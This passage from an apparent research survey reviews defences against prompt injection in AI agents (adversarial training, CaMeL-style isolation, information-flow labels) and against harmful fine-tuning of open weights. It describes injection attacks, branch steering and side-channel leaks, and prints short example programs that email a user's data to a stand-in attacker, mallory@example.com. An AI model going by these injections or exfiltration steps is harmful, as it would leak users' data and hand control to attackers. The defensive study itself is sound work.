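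4. The defender's reward for an attempt is the sum of the two scores. The attacker's reward for a task is the defender's average reward on it with the sign reversed.
5. Both models update their weights. Each becomes more likely to repeat what earned more than the average of its group and less likely to repeat what earned less.

In symbols, for a task with *K* attempts,

$$R_D=R_{\text{safety}}+R_{\text{utility}},\qquad R_A=-\frac{1}{K}\sum_{j=1}^{K}R_D^{(j)}$$

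Suppose the defender tries a task four times. Twice it stays safe and finishes, once it stays safe but gives up, and once it does something harmful and doesn't finish. Its rewards are 2, 2, 0 and −2, and the attacker gets the negative of their average, −0.5. This reward stops the defender from learning that refusing everything is best, but an agent that leaks a file and also completes the user's task scores 0, the same as one that safely gives up.

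The attacker's reward is highest when the defender fails every attempt, but then all the attempts score the same and the defender learns nothing from comparing them. Wang and colleagues therefore give more weight to tasks with mixed results when they update the two models.

The table compares the resulting model with the untrained model and with a defender trained against an attacker that stopped learning after its initial training. Lower numbers are better in every row except the last.

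| Measure | Untrained | Attacker fixed | Attacker learns |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent-SafetyBench, attack success | 49.1% | 31.0% | 17.8% |
| AgentHarm, harm score | 50.4 | 30.0 | 6.5 |
| MCP Security Bench, attack success | 60.4% | 38.6% | 31.3% |
| AgentDojo, attack success | 22.2% | 6.7% | 6.2% |
| AgentDojo, user's task completed under attack | 53.6% | 61.4% | 66.5% |

A learning attacker helped a lot on AgentHarm, which measures whether an agent goes along with harmful requests, but hardly at all against AgentDojo's prompt injections, where training against the fixed attacker had already produced most of the improvement. The defender kept its ordinary abilities, and some improved. Its accuracy rose from 30.3% to 43.7% on a test of planning and from 21.8% to 48.0% on a test of using several tools in sequence, and hardly changed on a test of calling functions correctly. Image classifiers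 usually lose accuracy in adversarial training, but here the attacker's tasks also gave the agent practice in using tools.

These benchmarks use attacks written in advance. Wang and colleagues also tested their attacker against the defender on 100 new seeds. The final attacker succeeded 92.6% of the time against the untrained model and 49.8% against the final defender, which had been trained to resist it. Training also raised the attacker's success rate against models it had not encountered in training, from 43.7% to 80.7% on a 70-billion-parameter Llama and from 12.3% to 22.5% on GPT-5.

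### Google's experience with Gemini

Google has published the most detailed account of adversarial training in a deployed language model. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (Shi, Lin and colleagues, 2025) describes how Gemini 2.5 was trained to ignore instructions hidden in material such as emails.

They generated many realistic conversations with different tools and different kinds of private data. They then ran several automated attacks on the model and used the successful injections as seeds to generate thousands more. To get the right answer for each attacked conversation, they warned the model not to reveal private information and kept only the answers in which it did the user's task and ignored the injection. The deployed model learned to give those answers without the warning. Its training also included reinforcement learning, which doesn't need example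 answers.

Gemini 2.5 appeared much more robust than Gemini 2.0 in a test with stored attacks. Of 1,799 prompts with injections optimised against Gemini 2.0, 92% worked on Gemini 2.0 and 18% on Gemini 2.5. Shi and colleagues then optimised new attacks against Gemini 2.5. The attacker tried to make the agent send out the user's passport number by email or through a calendar event.

| Adaptive attack | Email, Gemini 2.0 | Email, Gemini 2.5 | Calendar, Gemini 2.0 | Calendar, Gemini 2.5 |
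|---|---|---|---|---|
| Branching search by a language model (TAP) | 99.8% | 53.6% | 100% | 94.6% |
| Attacker model guided by estimated scores | 66.2% | 40.8% | 96.8% | 59.6% |
| Search over random tokens | 74.8% | 4.2% | 98.6% | 0% |

The average fall is 47 percentage points, but very uneven. Training nearly eliminated the success of attacks made of random tokens, while attacks in natural language kept much of their effectiveness. The branching search's success rate fell 46 points on the email tool, which Google had used in training, but only 5 points on the calendar tool, which it had held back. The comparison can't isolate the effect of the training, because Gemini 2.5 was also a more capable model. Shi and colleagues found that models better at following instructions are sometimes easier to attack, and suspect that this offset some of the gain.

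The trained model showed no noticeable loss of ordinary ability, and it scored as well as other leading models on a public leaderboard where people compare chatbots' answers. The attack figures are for the model alone, without the further safeguards in Google's products.

### OpenAI's trained attackers

ChatGPT Atlas is a web browser with an agent that can click, type and read pages on the user's behalf. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an attacker that the company trained by reinforcement learning to hijack this agent. Before committing to an injection, the attacker can test it in a simulator, which returns everything the agent would think and do. The attacker then revises the injection and tries again. This gives it an advantage over outside attackers, who can't see the agent's full reasoning.

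The attacker learned to lead the agent through harmful workflows of tens or hundreds of steps. In one example, it planted an email in a user's inbox. When the user asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent read the email and sent the user's chief executive a resignation letter instead. OpenAI trained a new version of the agent on the attacks that still worked, released it to all Atlas users and used the findings to improve its monitoring and other safeguards. The account shows that a trained attacker finds serious failures, but it gives no success rates from before or after the retraining, so we can't tell how many of those failures the retraining removed. OpenAI doubts that prompt injection will ever be fully solved.

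In July 2026, OpenAI gave figures for a later attacker, GPT-Red. According to SiliconANGLE (2026), GPT-Red earned rewards for successful attacks, while the defending models earned them for resisting and finishing their tasks. The Decoder's *OpenAI is now using AI to attack its own AI* reports that GPT-Red succeeded in 84% of test scenarios, compared with 13% for human attackers. It also reports that GPT-5.6 Sol, which learned from GPT-Red's attacks, failed about a sixth as often on direct prompt injections. In the earlier competition that Nasr and colleagues ran, people did better than an automated search.

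Wallace and colleagues say that OpenAI's newest models had already reached the maximum scores on the usual robustness tests, so a strong attacker is needed for measurement as well as training. OpenAI also used its latest internal attackers to check that GPT-6 Astra resists jailbreaks better than GPT-5.6 Sol. If a company trains and tests a model with similar attackers, the model may do well partly because it has learned to resist those attackers in particular.

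### When an attacker repeats one trick

Reinforcement learning rewards an attacker for succeeding, so once the attacker finds a trick that works, training does little to make it find another. It can reuse the same trick on every task in slightly different words, which researchers call mode collapse. The defender then trains on thousands of attacks but learns to resist only a few kinds.

He et al. observed this in their June 2026 study. They trained Qwen3-4B on a set of fixed attacks and on attacks that RL-Hammer, a published method, had found against it. The RL-Hammer attacks clustered around two templates. On average, the training lowered the success rate of fixed attacks it hadn't included from 33.3% to 19.6%. But the success rate of one unfamiliar family of attacks rose from 25.7% to 30.7%, and the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed fell from 61.9% to 49.5%. A genetic search,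 set up like the one Nasr et al. used, then succeeded 40.0% of the time, compared with 57.5% against the untrained model, so the training had removed less than a third of its successes.

Five months later, in *PIPETTE*, the same group (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested whether training on a more successful attacker's injections makes a model more robust. They ran two trained attackers, RL-Hammer and PISmith, against Qwen3-4B on 560 practice tasks. PISmith hijacked the agent on 68.8% of the tasks and collected 7,132 working injections, while RL-Hammer hijacked it on 33.4% and collected 4,282. The researchers trained one copy of the model on each collection and attacked both copies with three methods that neither had seen. They repeated this with a second model, Llama 3.1 8B, and with two ways of training, imitation of good answers and reinforcement learning. The table gives the highest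 success rate among the three attacks. Its last column is for a third attacker, which the researchers built themselves.

| Model and training | RL-Hammer's attacks | PISmith's attacks | PIPETTE's attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-4B, reinforcement learning | 27.5% | 47.5% | 20.0% |
| Qwen3-4B, imitation | 15.0% | 12.5% | 2.5% |
| Llama 3.1 8B, reinforcement learning | 25.0% | 27.5% | 10.0% |
| Llama 3.1 8B, imitation | 15.0% | 20.0% | 5.0% |

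PISmith's larger collection gave the weaker defence in three of the four cases, but each figure comes from only 40 tasks. The widest gap, 47.5% against 27.5%, is 19 hijacked tasks against 11, according to Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*. Two equally vulnerable models would differ by that much about one time in ten. In the other three cases, the gap between RL-Hammer and PISmith is one or two tasks. The results are good evidence that training on twice as many successful attacks doesn't make the defence much better, and weak evidence that it makes the defence worse. The rates also don't apply to ordinary use, because the 40 tasks were hard to defend. Simple attacks had already worked on all of them against the undefended Qwen3-4B.

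The low attack success rates after imitation training also need careful interpretation, because the agent may have become worse at completing any task, including the attacker's. Llama completed 40.2% of ordinary tasks before training and only about 16% after imitation training on either RL-Hammer's or PISmith's attacks.

### Rewarding new strategies

RL-Hammer and PISmith both have features meant to keep their attacks varied, but these features respond to wording. RL-Hammer's designers found that it could satisfy them by changing capital letters or adding irrelevant text. PIPETTE's attacker gets an extra reward for using a strategy that it hasn't used before. A language model describes how each successful injection misleads the agent, and the system condenses these descriptions into 32 basic strategies. Another model then grades how fully the known strategies explain a new injection *d*,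 on a scale that runs from 0 to 1. The extra reward is

$$r_{\text{cov}}=\Phi(d)\,\big(1-\mathrm{ES}(d)\big)$$

where Φ(*d*) is 1 if the injection works and 0 if it fails, and ES(*d*) is the grade. An injection that rewords a known trick might have a grade of 0.9 and earn 0.1, while a working injection that is mostly unexplained might earn 0.8. The system rebuilds the list every 25 training steps, so a new trick soon stops paying.

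On the same kind of grade, RL-Hammer's attacks on Qwen3-4B explained only about 0.20 of an unfamiliar family of attacks and soon stopped improving, while PIPETTE's reached about 0.60. This is consistent with variety making the difference but doesn't prove it. He and colleagues haven't checked the grading model against human judgement, and PIPETTE's attacker also collected the most injections of the three. In their June study, an earlier version of the reward had a modest effect. Defenders trained on the last batch of attacks let an unfamiliar attack through 20% of the time with the reward and 25% without it.

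PIPETTE also changes how the defender learns. The agent must check whether the material it has just read contains instructions, and whether its next action serves the user's request. Training also rewards tokens that would be more likely if the agent had been told to ignore the injection than if it had been told to obey it. On Qwen3-4B, the trained agent completed 65.0% of ordinary tasks, compared with 61.9% for the untrained model.

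The complete method did well against a genetic search that made up to 248 attempts per task. SecOPD, a rival defence, trains an agent to behave as it would without the injection.

| Model | No added defence | Rival trained defence | PIPETTE |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 8B | 17.5% | 12.5% (Meta SecAlign) | 2.5% |
| Qwen3.6-27B | 70.0% | 30.0% (SecOPD) | 5.0% |
| GPT-OSS-20B | 92.5% | – | 10.0% |

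A second adaptive attack against PIPETTE succeeded 0% to 5% of the time. This test again used 40 tasks, and the model that wrote the attacks had only 4 billion parameters. The attackers could see the agent's actions, but nobody told them how PIPETTE works or adapted their prompts to it. Nasr and colleagues' results suggest that a stronger attacker that knew how PIPETTE works would do better. The researchers also expect a larger budget to raise the success rate.

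### Different lessons from the same attacks

Even with identical training attacks, the result depends on what the developer asks the model to learn from them. Shah, Brinkmann and Angell (2026), in *Mitigating Adaptive Attacks against Reasoning Models with Activation Consistency Training*, compared two methods that both use pairs of prompts, one clean and one containing an attack. Output consistency training teaches the model to answer the attacked prompt as the original model answered the clean one, including all of its reasoning. Activation consistency training ignores the answer. It adjusts the model's activations on the attacked prompt to match the original model's on the clean prompt:

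$$L=\sum_{\ell}\sum_{t}\big\lVert h_\theta(p')[\ell,t]-h_{\theta_0}(p)[\ell,t]\big\rVert^2$$

Here *p* is the clean prompt, *p*′ the attacked one, and *h*[ℓ, *t*] the activations in layer ℓ at token *t*. The method compares activations only at the final tokens that both prompts share, usually about six formatting markers just before the model responds. It still simulates attacks, because the prompt pairs contain stored ones, though it doesn't search for new ones. It also takes little compute for reasoning models, because the developer doesn't have to train on thousands of tokens of reasoning.

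On GPT-OSS-20B, fixed prompt injections succeeded 4.4% of the time against output training and 29.6% against activation training. Shah and colleagues then used reinforcement learning to train an attacker against each defended model. These attackers succeeded 57.4% of the time against output training and 37.0% against activation training. The two comparisons used different benchmarks, which may explain some of the reversal, but output training was also slightly ahead on the fixed tests as a whole. A developer who had run only the fixed tests would have picked the method that did worse against an adaptive attacker.

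Activation training also made three of the other four models more robust to trained attackers than output training did. On the fourth, Phi-4-reasoning, output training resisted attacks better but reduced accuracy on ordinary tasks. Neither method withstood the attacks on Gemma 4. Activation training did better against jailbreaks. With only about 100 training pairs per model, it cut the trained attacker's success rate from nearly 100% to almost zero on three models.

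An earlier study by Irpan and colleagues offers a possible explanation. It found that output training moves the activations for clean and attacked prompts further apart, while activation training brings them closer together. A model that separates them may be detecting the attacks it was trained on, which would help less against new ones.

### When simulating an attacker helps

Training against a trained attacker can make a model much more robust than training on fixed attack templates. In their June study, He and colleagues trained Qwen3-4B on templates alone, and the genetic search still hijacked it on 20 of 40 tasks, compared with 23 for the untrained model. Training on attacks from an attacker rewarded for variety lowered the number to 7. That attacker was both stronger and more varied than the templates. PISmith was a stronger attacker than RL-Hammer, but training against it did not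 produce a more robust model, so strength seems to help mainly when it brings new strategies. Help Net Security sensibly advises companies that buy agents to ask how many distinct techniques the vendor tested, because most of the successful attacks in a vendor's count may repeat the same techniques.

The attacker also has to keep adapting as the defender changes. PIPETTE attacks only the original model, so it can't discover weaknesses that appear during retraining. Wang and colleagues tested the effect of continued learning without their special weighting of tasks. On Agent-SafetyBench, attacks succeeded 22.9% of the time against a model trained with an attacker that kept learning, compared with 31.0% when the attacker had stopped learning.

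The simulation must also match the real threat. Most research on prompt injection studies one injection in one session, but a real attacker can leave instructions in documents or an agent's memory that affect many later sessions. A defender trained only on single-session injections has not been trained to resist these persistent attacks.

Google's results show how much a defence can benefit from closely matching the test, even if it needs no attack search. In the calendar test, the branching search succeeded 94.6% of the time against the adversarially trained Gemini 2.5, but 10.8% of the time against Gemini 2.0 with only the added warning about private information. The warning had an advantage because it named exactly the harm that the test measured, and it could also stop an agent from sharing data when the user wants it to. With both defences, the attack succeeded 6.2% of the time. Shi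 and colleagues therefore treat adversarial training as one layer of protection and want others outside the model, where a persuasive injection can't disable them.

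## Can an agent be protected by limiting what untrusted text can do?

Websites once had a problem much like prompt injection. They pasted visitors' input into database commands, so an attacker could type a command into a form and the database would run it. Developers solved this by fixing the structure of each command before adding the input, not by getting better at recognising malicious input. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) draws this comparison but notes that a database language has a grammar that separates commands from data, while natural language has none. A language model therefore can't reliably separate the two itself, so ordinary software around the model has to do it.

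This kind of defence limits what an agent can do if an injection fools the model. In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) set out the principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted text, that text must be unable to trigger any action with harmful effects. Designers can build such a defence without examples of attacks, so it is attacker-free. It also doesn't rely on the model to obey a prompt asking it to ignore strangers' instructions.

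### How CaMeL works

The best-known system of this kind is CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind proposed in 2025. It extends Simon Willison's idea of dividing an agent between two language models, a privileged one that plans and a quarantined one that reads. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it handles a request:

1. The privileged model reads the user's request and writes a short program in a restricted form of Python. The program sets out which tools to call, in what order, and what to do with the results.
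2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and calls the tools.
3. When the program needs something from untrusted text, the interpreter passes the text to the quarantined model. This model has no tools and can only return a value, which the interpreter stores without showing it to the privileged model.
4. The interpreter attaches a record to every value, listing where it came from and who may read it. Values computed from other values carry their records along.
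5. Before each tool call, a policy checks the call, its inputs and their records, and allows or refuses it.

Suppose a user writes: "Send the budget file to Bob. His address is in his last email." The privileged model might write this program:

```
email = read_last_email(sender="Bob")
address = ask_quarantined_model("What is Bob's address?", email)
budget = get_file("budget.xlsx")
send_email(to=address, attachment=budget)
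```

Bob's email quotes an attacker's message with an instruction to send all the user's files to mallory@example.com. The privileged model wrote the program before anyone opened the email, so no line of the program sends the other files. The instruction may fool the quarantined model that reads it, but that model has no tool for sending anything.

The attacker can still try to change a value. If the quoted message claims that Bob's new address is mallory@example.com, the quarantined model may return that address, and the last line would then send the budget to the attacker. The program would be running exactly as written. This is what the records are for:

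| Value | Where it came from | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| `address` (mallory@example.com) | Bob's email, through the quarantined model | the user, Bob |
| `budget` | the user's files | the user, Bob |

If the policy allows an attachment to go only to people who may read it, the interpreter refuses the call because Mallory isn't one of them. It would allow a call with Bob's real address. A stricter policy might require every recipient's address to come from a trusted source. That would also stop the attack, but it would block the task even when there is no attack, since Bob's real address comes from the email.

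### Labels and design patterns

CaMeL's records are a form of information-flow control, an established technique in computer security. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) uses it in FIDES, an agent developed at Microsoft. FIDES gives every piece of data two labels, one for whether it is trusted and one for who may read it. Anything derived from untrusted data is also untrusted. If Ana, Bob and Cem may read one document, and Bob, Cem and Dee may read another, only Bob and Cem may read a summary of both.

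FIDES chooses its actions one at a time, whereas CaMeL writes the whole program in advance. FIDES stores untrusted text in variables that the model choosing the actions can pass to tools without reading. When a task depends on what the text contains, such as "add a meeting to my calendar if one of these emails asks for one", FIDES can put a yes-or-no question to a quarantined model and reveal only the answer. An attacker could make the answer wrong, but a "yes" or "no" is too short to carry a new instruction.

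Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe six design patterns, which give up different amounts of flexibility. In the strictest, the model picks from a fixed list of actions and never receives the results, so they can't influence it. In another, an agent looking for invoices uses a separate model for each file, and each model outputs only whether its file is an invoice. A malicious file can still be wrongly counted as an invoice, but it can't affect how the agent treats the other files. CaMeL's pattern, a program written in advance, is among the more flexible. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees while they depend on current language models, so they advise developers to build agents for narrower jobs.

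### Security and usefulness on AgentDojo

According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks under attack with OpenAI's o3 model, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and no injection covered by its threat model succeeded. CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many tokens as the undefended agent.

Later tests by other groups also found strong security, but usefulness fell much more. In *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a rival defence, an adapted version of CaMeL stopped all 629 attacks but completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) ran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each, with and without its policies. The table combines their two classes of attack and counts only the runs that finished.

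| Model | Policies | Ordinary tasks completed | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | off | 66.7% | 1 of 240 |
| GPT-5.2 | on | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | off | 70.8% | 4 of 382 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | on | 37.5% | 0 of 357 |

Even without any policies, separating the two models stopped nearly every attack. In about two thirds of the task-attack pairs, the attack needed a tool call or file that the user's task would never involve. Adding the policies stopped the few remaining attacks but reduced the number of completed tasks by almost half. The policies might stop more attacks by someone who adapts to CaMeL, who would concentrate on changing values.

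One of the successful attacks exploited a task in which the user asks the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it precisely. The privileged model wrote a program that could turn each instruction into a tool call, which gave control to whoever had written the file.

Garby and colleagues' own agent recovers much of the lost usefulness. Its planning model can approve particular uses of untrusted data before it has seen any. The agent completed 65% to 75% of ordinary tasks, depending on the model, and 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had told the agent to pay a bill described in a text file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents.

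FIDES has a similar trade-off. With GPT-4o, 152 injections succeeded against a basic agent and none against FIDES with its policies on. But the share of ordinary tasks completed fell from 98.8% to 52.5% in banking and from 75% to 59% in office work. The security result depends on near-perfect labelling, because Costa and colleagues marked a type of data as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it. A company labelling its own data wouldn't have a list of the attacks it would face.

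CaMeL reduces task completion less for more capable models. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) applied CaMeL without policies to teams of agents doing industrial maintenance tasks. Task completion fell by 21.6 percentage points on average across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5.

The approach is harder to apply to agents with less predictable tools. An agent that operates a computer through its screen normally looks at the screen before every action, which a planner isolated from untrusted content can't do. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, had the privileged model write a program with a branch for each situation it might meet. These programs averaged 41 tool calls, compared with 5 on AgentDojo, and the agent kept at most 57% of leading models' performance. *INFUSE* adapted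 CaMeL's approach to command-line agents and found no clear reduction in successful attacks. The paper limits this conclusion to its own adaptation.

### What the guarantee leaves open

CaMeL is designed to stop untrusted text from adding a step to the program, but it doesn't ensure that the text is true. If a user asks an agent to email today's schedule to their boss, an injection in the calendar can't change the recipient, but it can change the content of the message. Costa and colleagues give the example of an email that tells the quarantined model to produce an empty summary.

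False content can also do harm through the action the user requested. *Beyond Instruction Override* (Zhang, Bertran and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that settles disputes between buyers and sellers. The platform's records support a refund of $899.99, but the buyer's evidence cites an invented policy that would raise it to $1,074.99. The agent is supposed to issue a refund, so restricting which tools it can use doesn't help. In the paper's tests, such attacks succeeded 17.0% of the time without a defence and 15.4% with a defence that checks tool calls against a policy. CaMeL can require the amount to come from the platform's own records, but a free-text field, such as a note explaining the decision, is much harder to restrict this way.

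Programs with many branches have a related weakness, which Foerster and colleagues call branch steering. Suppose the program includes a step to dismiss any cookie notice. An attacker can buy an advertisement that looks like a cookie notice, and the agent will click it and go to the attacker's website. The attacker doesn't need to add an instruction because the program already includes the click.

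Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, built 101 tasks to test this. The attacks succeeded 94.4% of the time against an ordinary agent and 89.5% against one that only separated the two models. Their defence, COBRA, also fixes in advance which websites, tools and values each branch may use. It reduced attack success to 0% and kept 97% of the two-model agent's performance on ordinary tasks. But an attack counts as successful only if the harmful action breaks a limit in force at that moment, so the benchmark doesn't measure harm that the limits allow. The attacker also couldn't see the plan or adapt to it.

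Side channels are another gap. They reveal a secret through the program's behaviour instead of sending it directly. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL marks a variable as secret only if the program actually changes it in a step that depends on a secret. A program like this one can therefore leak whether a bank balance is above $10,000:

```
flag = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000: flag = False
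if flag: rich = False
if rich: send_email("mallory@example.com", "rich")
```

If the balance is high, the third line changes `flag` and CaMeL marks it as secret. The fourth line then leaves `rich` unchanged and unmarked, so the email goes out. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. Mallory can therefore tell whether the balance is high by whether the email arrives. This is a gap in CaMeL's guarantee more than a ready-made attack, because the privileged model would have to write such a program and it never reads the attacker's text. CaMeL also retries after a policy blocks a run, and Garby and colleagues show that repeated retries could leak a secret one bit at a time.

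Finally, the defence depends on correct labels and policies. CaMeL trusts the user's request, which may include text the user has copied from an attacker's website. Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL's interpreter treated untrusted values as trusted once a program had inserted them into a longer piece of text.

Labels can also get lost between agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues asked a team of three CaMeL agents to send a summary of job applicants to a colleague, Julie, on Slack. The applicant database contained an instruction to email the data to an outside address. The first agent fetched the data and the coordinating agent had it summarised, and the instruction didn't affect either agent's program. But the coordinating agent then put the summary into its request to the third agent, whose privileged model treats requests as trusted. The third agent sent the data to Julie and to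 the attacker. Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed this by passing untrusted values between agents separately from the instructions. In a larger test, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time on average without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent, and never with the fix.

### Structural and measured protection under adaptive attack

Most of these results come from attacks written in advance, and Narisetty and colleagues warn that defences based on prompts and filters once looked strong in similar tests. They tried an adaptive attack on Progent, which checks each tool call against a list of permissions. Progent cut the success rate of fixed attacks from 25.8% to 4.2%, and the adaptive attack succeeded against it 2.6% of the time. This evidence is encouraging but limited, since they used one hand-written adaptive attack and a small model.

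In *Composable Trust for Language Models*, Shkolnikov (2026) tested a structural rule and a measured defence in the same system. The structural rule ranks each input by the channel it arrives on, with the operator's instructions first, followed by the user's request, retrieved documents and web pages. Anything that combines several inputs takes the lowest rank among them, and an action goes ahead only if the inputs controlling it rank high enough. Shkolnikov checked 8,729 combinations of inputs and extended the result to combinations of any size, proving that low-ranked text can't authorise an action.

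The tested defence protects the text of the answer. The model first rewrites lower-ranked material as plain facts without commands, then answers with each source marked by rank. Shkolnikov tuned the prompts for both steps on a set that included 100 attacks, so this half of the system, unlike the structural rule, uses an attacker signal. On new fixed attacks, the defence raised the share of injections resisted from 27% to 94%, but quality on ordinary tasks fell from 77% to 73%.

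Shkolnikov then had another model adapt its attacks to the system, and in some tests that model had detailed knowledge of the defence. The structural rule let through no unauthorised action in 12 attempts. This alone is weak evidence, because a rule that failed one time in five would still get through 12 attempts without a failure about 7% of the time. The proof is a better reason to trust the rule, provided that the operator assigns every input to the right channel.

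The tested defence resisted 87% of the adaptive attacks, down from 94%. With 30 scenarios for each type of attacker, the true figure could be from 70% to 95%, so the size of the drop is uncertain. The successful attacks changed the answer's content or form, for example by turning it into a haiku, but none caused an action. Such failures are serious when users act on what the system writes, but minor for an agent whose main risk is sending money to the wrong person.

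## Do open-weight models resist harmful fine-tuning better if training simulates the attack?

Anyone who downloads a model's weights can run the model without the software that limits what an agent can do, and can also retrain it. A developer who publishes weights therefore has to build the protection into the weights themselves, and can't later fix a weakness in copies people already have.

*Defending Against Malicious Finetuning by Scaling Train-Time Adversarial Attacks* (2026) cites earlier research which found that training on ten harmful questions and answers can be enough to remove a model's refusals. The attacker also has more freedom than in most image tests, where the threat model limits how much each pixel can change. Zloczower, Lenga and colleagues (2026), in *A Few Steps Further*, point out that the developer acts once, before release. The attacker then studies the finished weights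 and chooses the data, the training method and the number of steps, which can exceed the number the developer prepared for.

The attacker's one constraint is that the model must stay capable, because a model that answers harmful requests with nonsense is useless to them. Some defences therefore try to keep the model from becoming harmful, and others try to make it lose its abilities as it becomes harmful.

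### TAR and Booster

TAR, which Tamirisa and colleagues proposed in 2024, applies the idea of adversarial training to a model's weights. The version that protects refusals works as follows:

1. Copy the current model and fine-tune the copy on harmful examples. The published recipe uses 64 steps and varies the learning rate, which sets the size of each step.
2. At every fourth step of this inner loop, measure how strongly the copy still prefers a refusal to a harmful answer.
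3. In the outer loop, adjust the original model so that an attacked copy would keep more of that preference. Train on ordinary material too, so that the model stays useful.
4. Discard the copy and attack the adjusted model again.

Zloczower and colleagues write defences of this type as

$$L(\theta)=L_{\text{align}}(\theta)+\lambda R(\theta'),\qquad \theta'=\text{SimAttack}(\theta)$$

Here θ stands for the released weights and θ′ for the weights after the simulated attack. *L*_align is the loss from ordinary training for safety and usefulness. *R* penalizes whatever the developer doesn't want the attacked model to do, and λ sets the strength of that penalty.

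Booster, from Huang and colleagues, needs less computing because it simulates a single harmful step. Its penalty is the amount by which that step would improve the model's fit to harmful answers:

$$R=L_h(\theta)-L_h(\theta')$$

*L*ₕ is the loss on harmful answers. If one step of harmful fine-tuning would lower it from 2.0 to 1.6, the penalty is 0.4, and training adjusts the weights so that the step lowers the loss less. This slows the start of an attack, but the penalty doesn't measure the effect of the hundredth step.

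### Weighting the attacker's data

Hu, Shen and colleagues (2025), in *Adaptive Defense against Harmful Fine-Tuning for Large Language Models*, give three arguments against simulating attacks during training. Developers can't anticipate every attack, so they simulate only a narrow range. A defence prepared in advance also can't adjust to the actual attack, whose data might be 5% harmful or 90%. Finally, simulation needs a set of harmful examples, which is hard to build without knowing what the attacker will use.

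Their alternative, the Bayesian Data Scheduler, is for companies that fine-tune a model on data their customers upload. The company trains the model on the upload and on its own safe examples, which pair harmful requests with refusals. At the same time, it learns a weight for every uploaded example. Leaving out random noise and constants, the weight *w*ᵢ of example *i* changes in proportion to

$$-s_i\Big(\ell_i-\sum_k s_k\ell_k\Big)$$

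where ℓᵢ is the model's loss on the example and *s*ᵢ is the example's current share of the total weight. Suppose that three examples have equal weights and losses of 0.5, 0.7 and 2.4. The average is 1.2, so the first two gain weight and the third loses it. Harmful examples tend to lose weight because they conflict with the refusals that the model is learning alongside them.

When 10% of the uploaded data was harmful, the fine-tuned model gave harmful answers 1.2% of the time, compared with 8.3% for Booster. When 50% was harmful, the model's rate was still 1.2%, while Booster's rose to 77.2%. Booster's increase supports the first two arguments. The third is weaker because Hu and colleagues took their harmful test data from BeaverTails, a public collection that a developer could also use for simulation.

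The comparison also favours the scheduler because it works during fine-tuning and can inspect the upload, while Booster finishes before the upload arrives. The scheduler is attacker-free in that building it takes no examples of attacks, but part of the reason it can do without a simulated attack is that it receives the real one. An attacker who knew the method would have reason to look for harmful examples that a safety-trained model fits easily, since the scheduler would not reduce their weight.

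### Filtering the pretraining data

Developers can also keep dangerous knowledge out of a model from the start. In *Deep Ignorance*, O'Brien, Casper and colleagues (2025) removed texts about biology that could be used in weapons from the pretraining data, the text from which a language model first learns, and trained models with 6.9 billion parameters on the rest. Filtering needs no attacker signal, but the developer has to decide which knowledge is dangerous. Russinovich (2026) notes in *Fool's Gold* that filtering can't protect an already trained model.

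The table shows who has to apply each defence. PATCHER is a newer method that simulates a longer attack.

| Defence | Simulates an attack | Who applies it, and when | Can protect released weights |
|---|---|---|---|
| TAR, Booster, PATCHER | yes | the developer, before release | yes |
| Pretraining data filtering | no | the developer, before pretraining | yes |
| Bayesian Data Scheduler | no | the company that runs the fine-tuning, during it | no |

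The scheduler can't protect released weights because an attacker who runs the training would simply leave it out.

### When the attacker keeps training

Zloczower and colleagues surveyed fifteen defences, including TAR and Booster, and concluded that each is designed for a limited attacker. Some are designed for small changes to the weights or activations and others for a short simulated attack, but an attacker can exceed those limits once the model is released.

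They tested six of the fifteen defences on four open models with 7 or 8 billion parameters. Vaccine, VAA and a method for unlearning dangerous knowledge train the model to withstand small, harmful changes to its activations or weights. Booster and CTRAP simulate a harmful training step, and CTRAP also trains the model to break down after it. SDD trains the model to give fluent but irrelevant answers to harmful requests, without simulating an attack. Fine-tuning the model to replace those answers is meant to damage its ability to follow instructions.

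The attack was ordinary fine-tuning, with three passes over 9,000 harmful examples, 3,375 steps in total. Across three learning rates, there were 72 runs on defended models. An automated judge scored harmfulness from 0 to 1, and 600 multiple-choice questions measured capability.

Harmfulness was higher at the end than at release in all 72 runs, by 0.372 on average. The smallest increase was only 0.022, however, so an increase alone is weak evidence that a defence eroded. Comparing defended models with undefended ones is more informative. On Llama 3.1 at the highest learning rate, the six defended models ended between 0.515 and 0.527, and the undefended one at 0.528. The six included SDD, which doesn't simulate an attack, so simulating a harmful step gave Booster and CTRAP no lasting advantage over it there.

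Other models gave more varied results. The table shows four runs, all at the highest learning rate.

| Defence and model | Harmfulness after the attack | Capability at release | Capability after the attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Vaccine, Llama 2 | 0.393 | 45.1% | 53.7% |
| CTRAP, Zephyr | 0.521 | 57.4% | 50.1% |
| VAA, Qwen3 | 0.241 | 45.5% | 25.5% |
| VAA, Zephyr | at most 0.069 | 42.5% | 37.8% |

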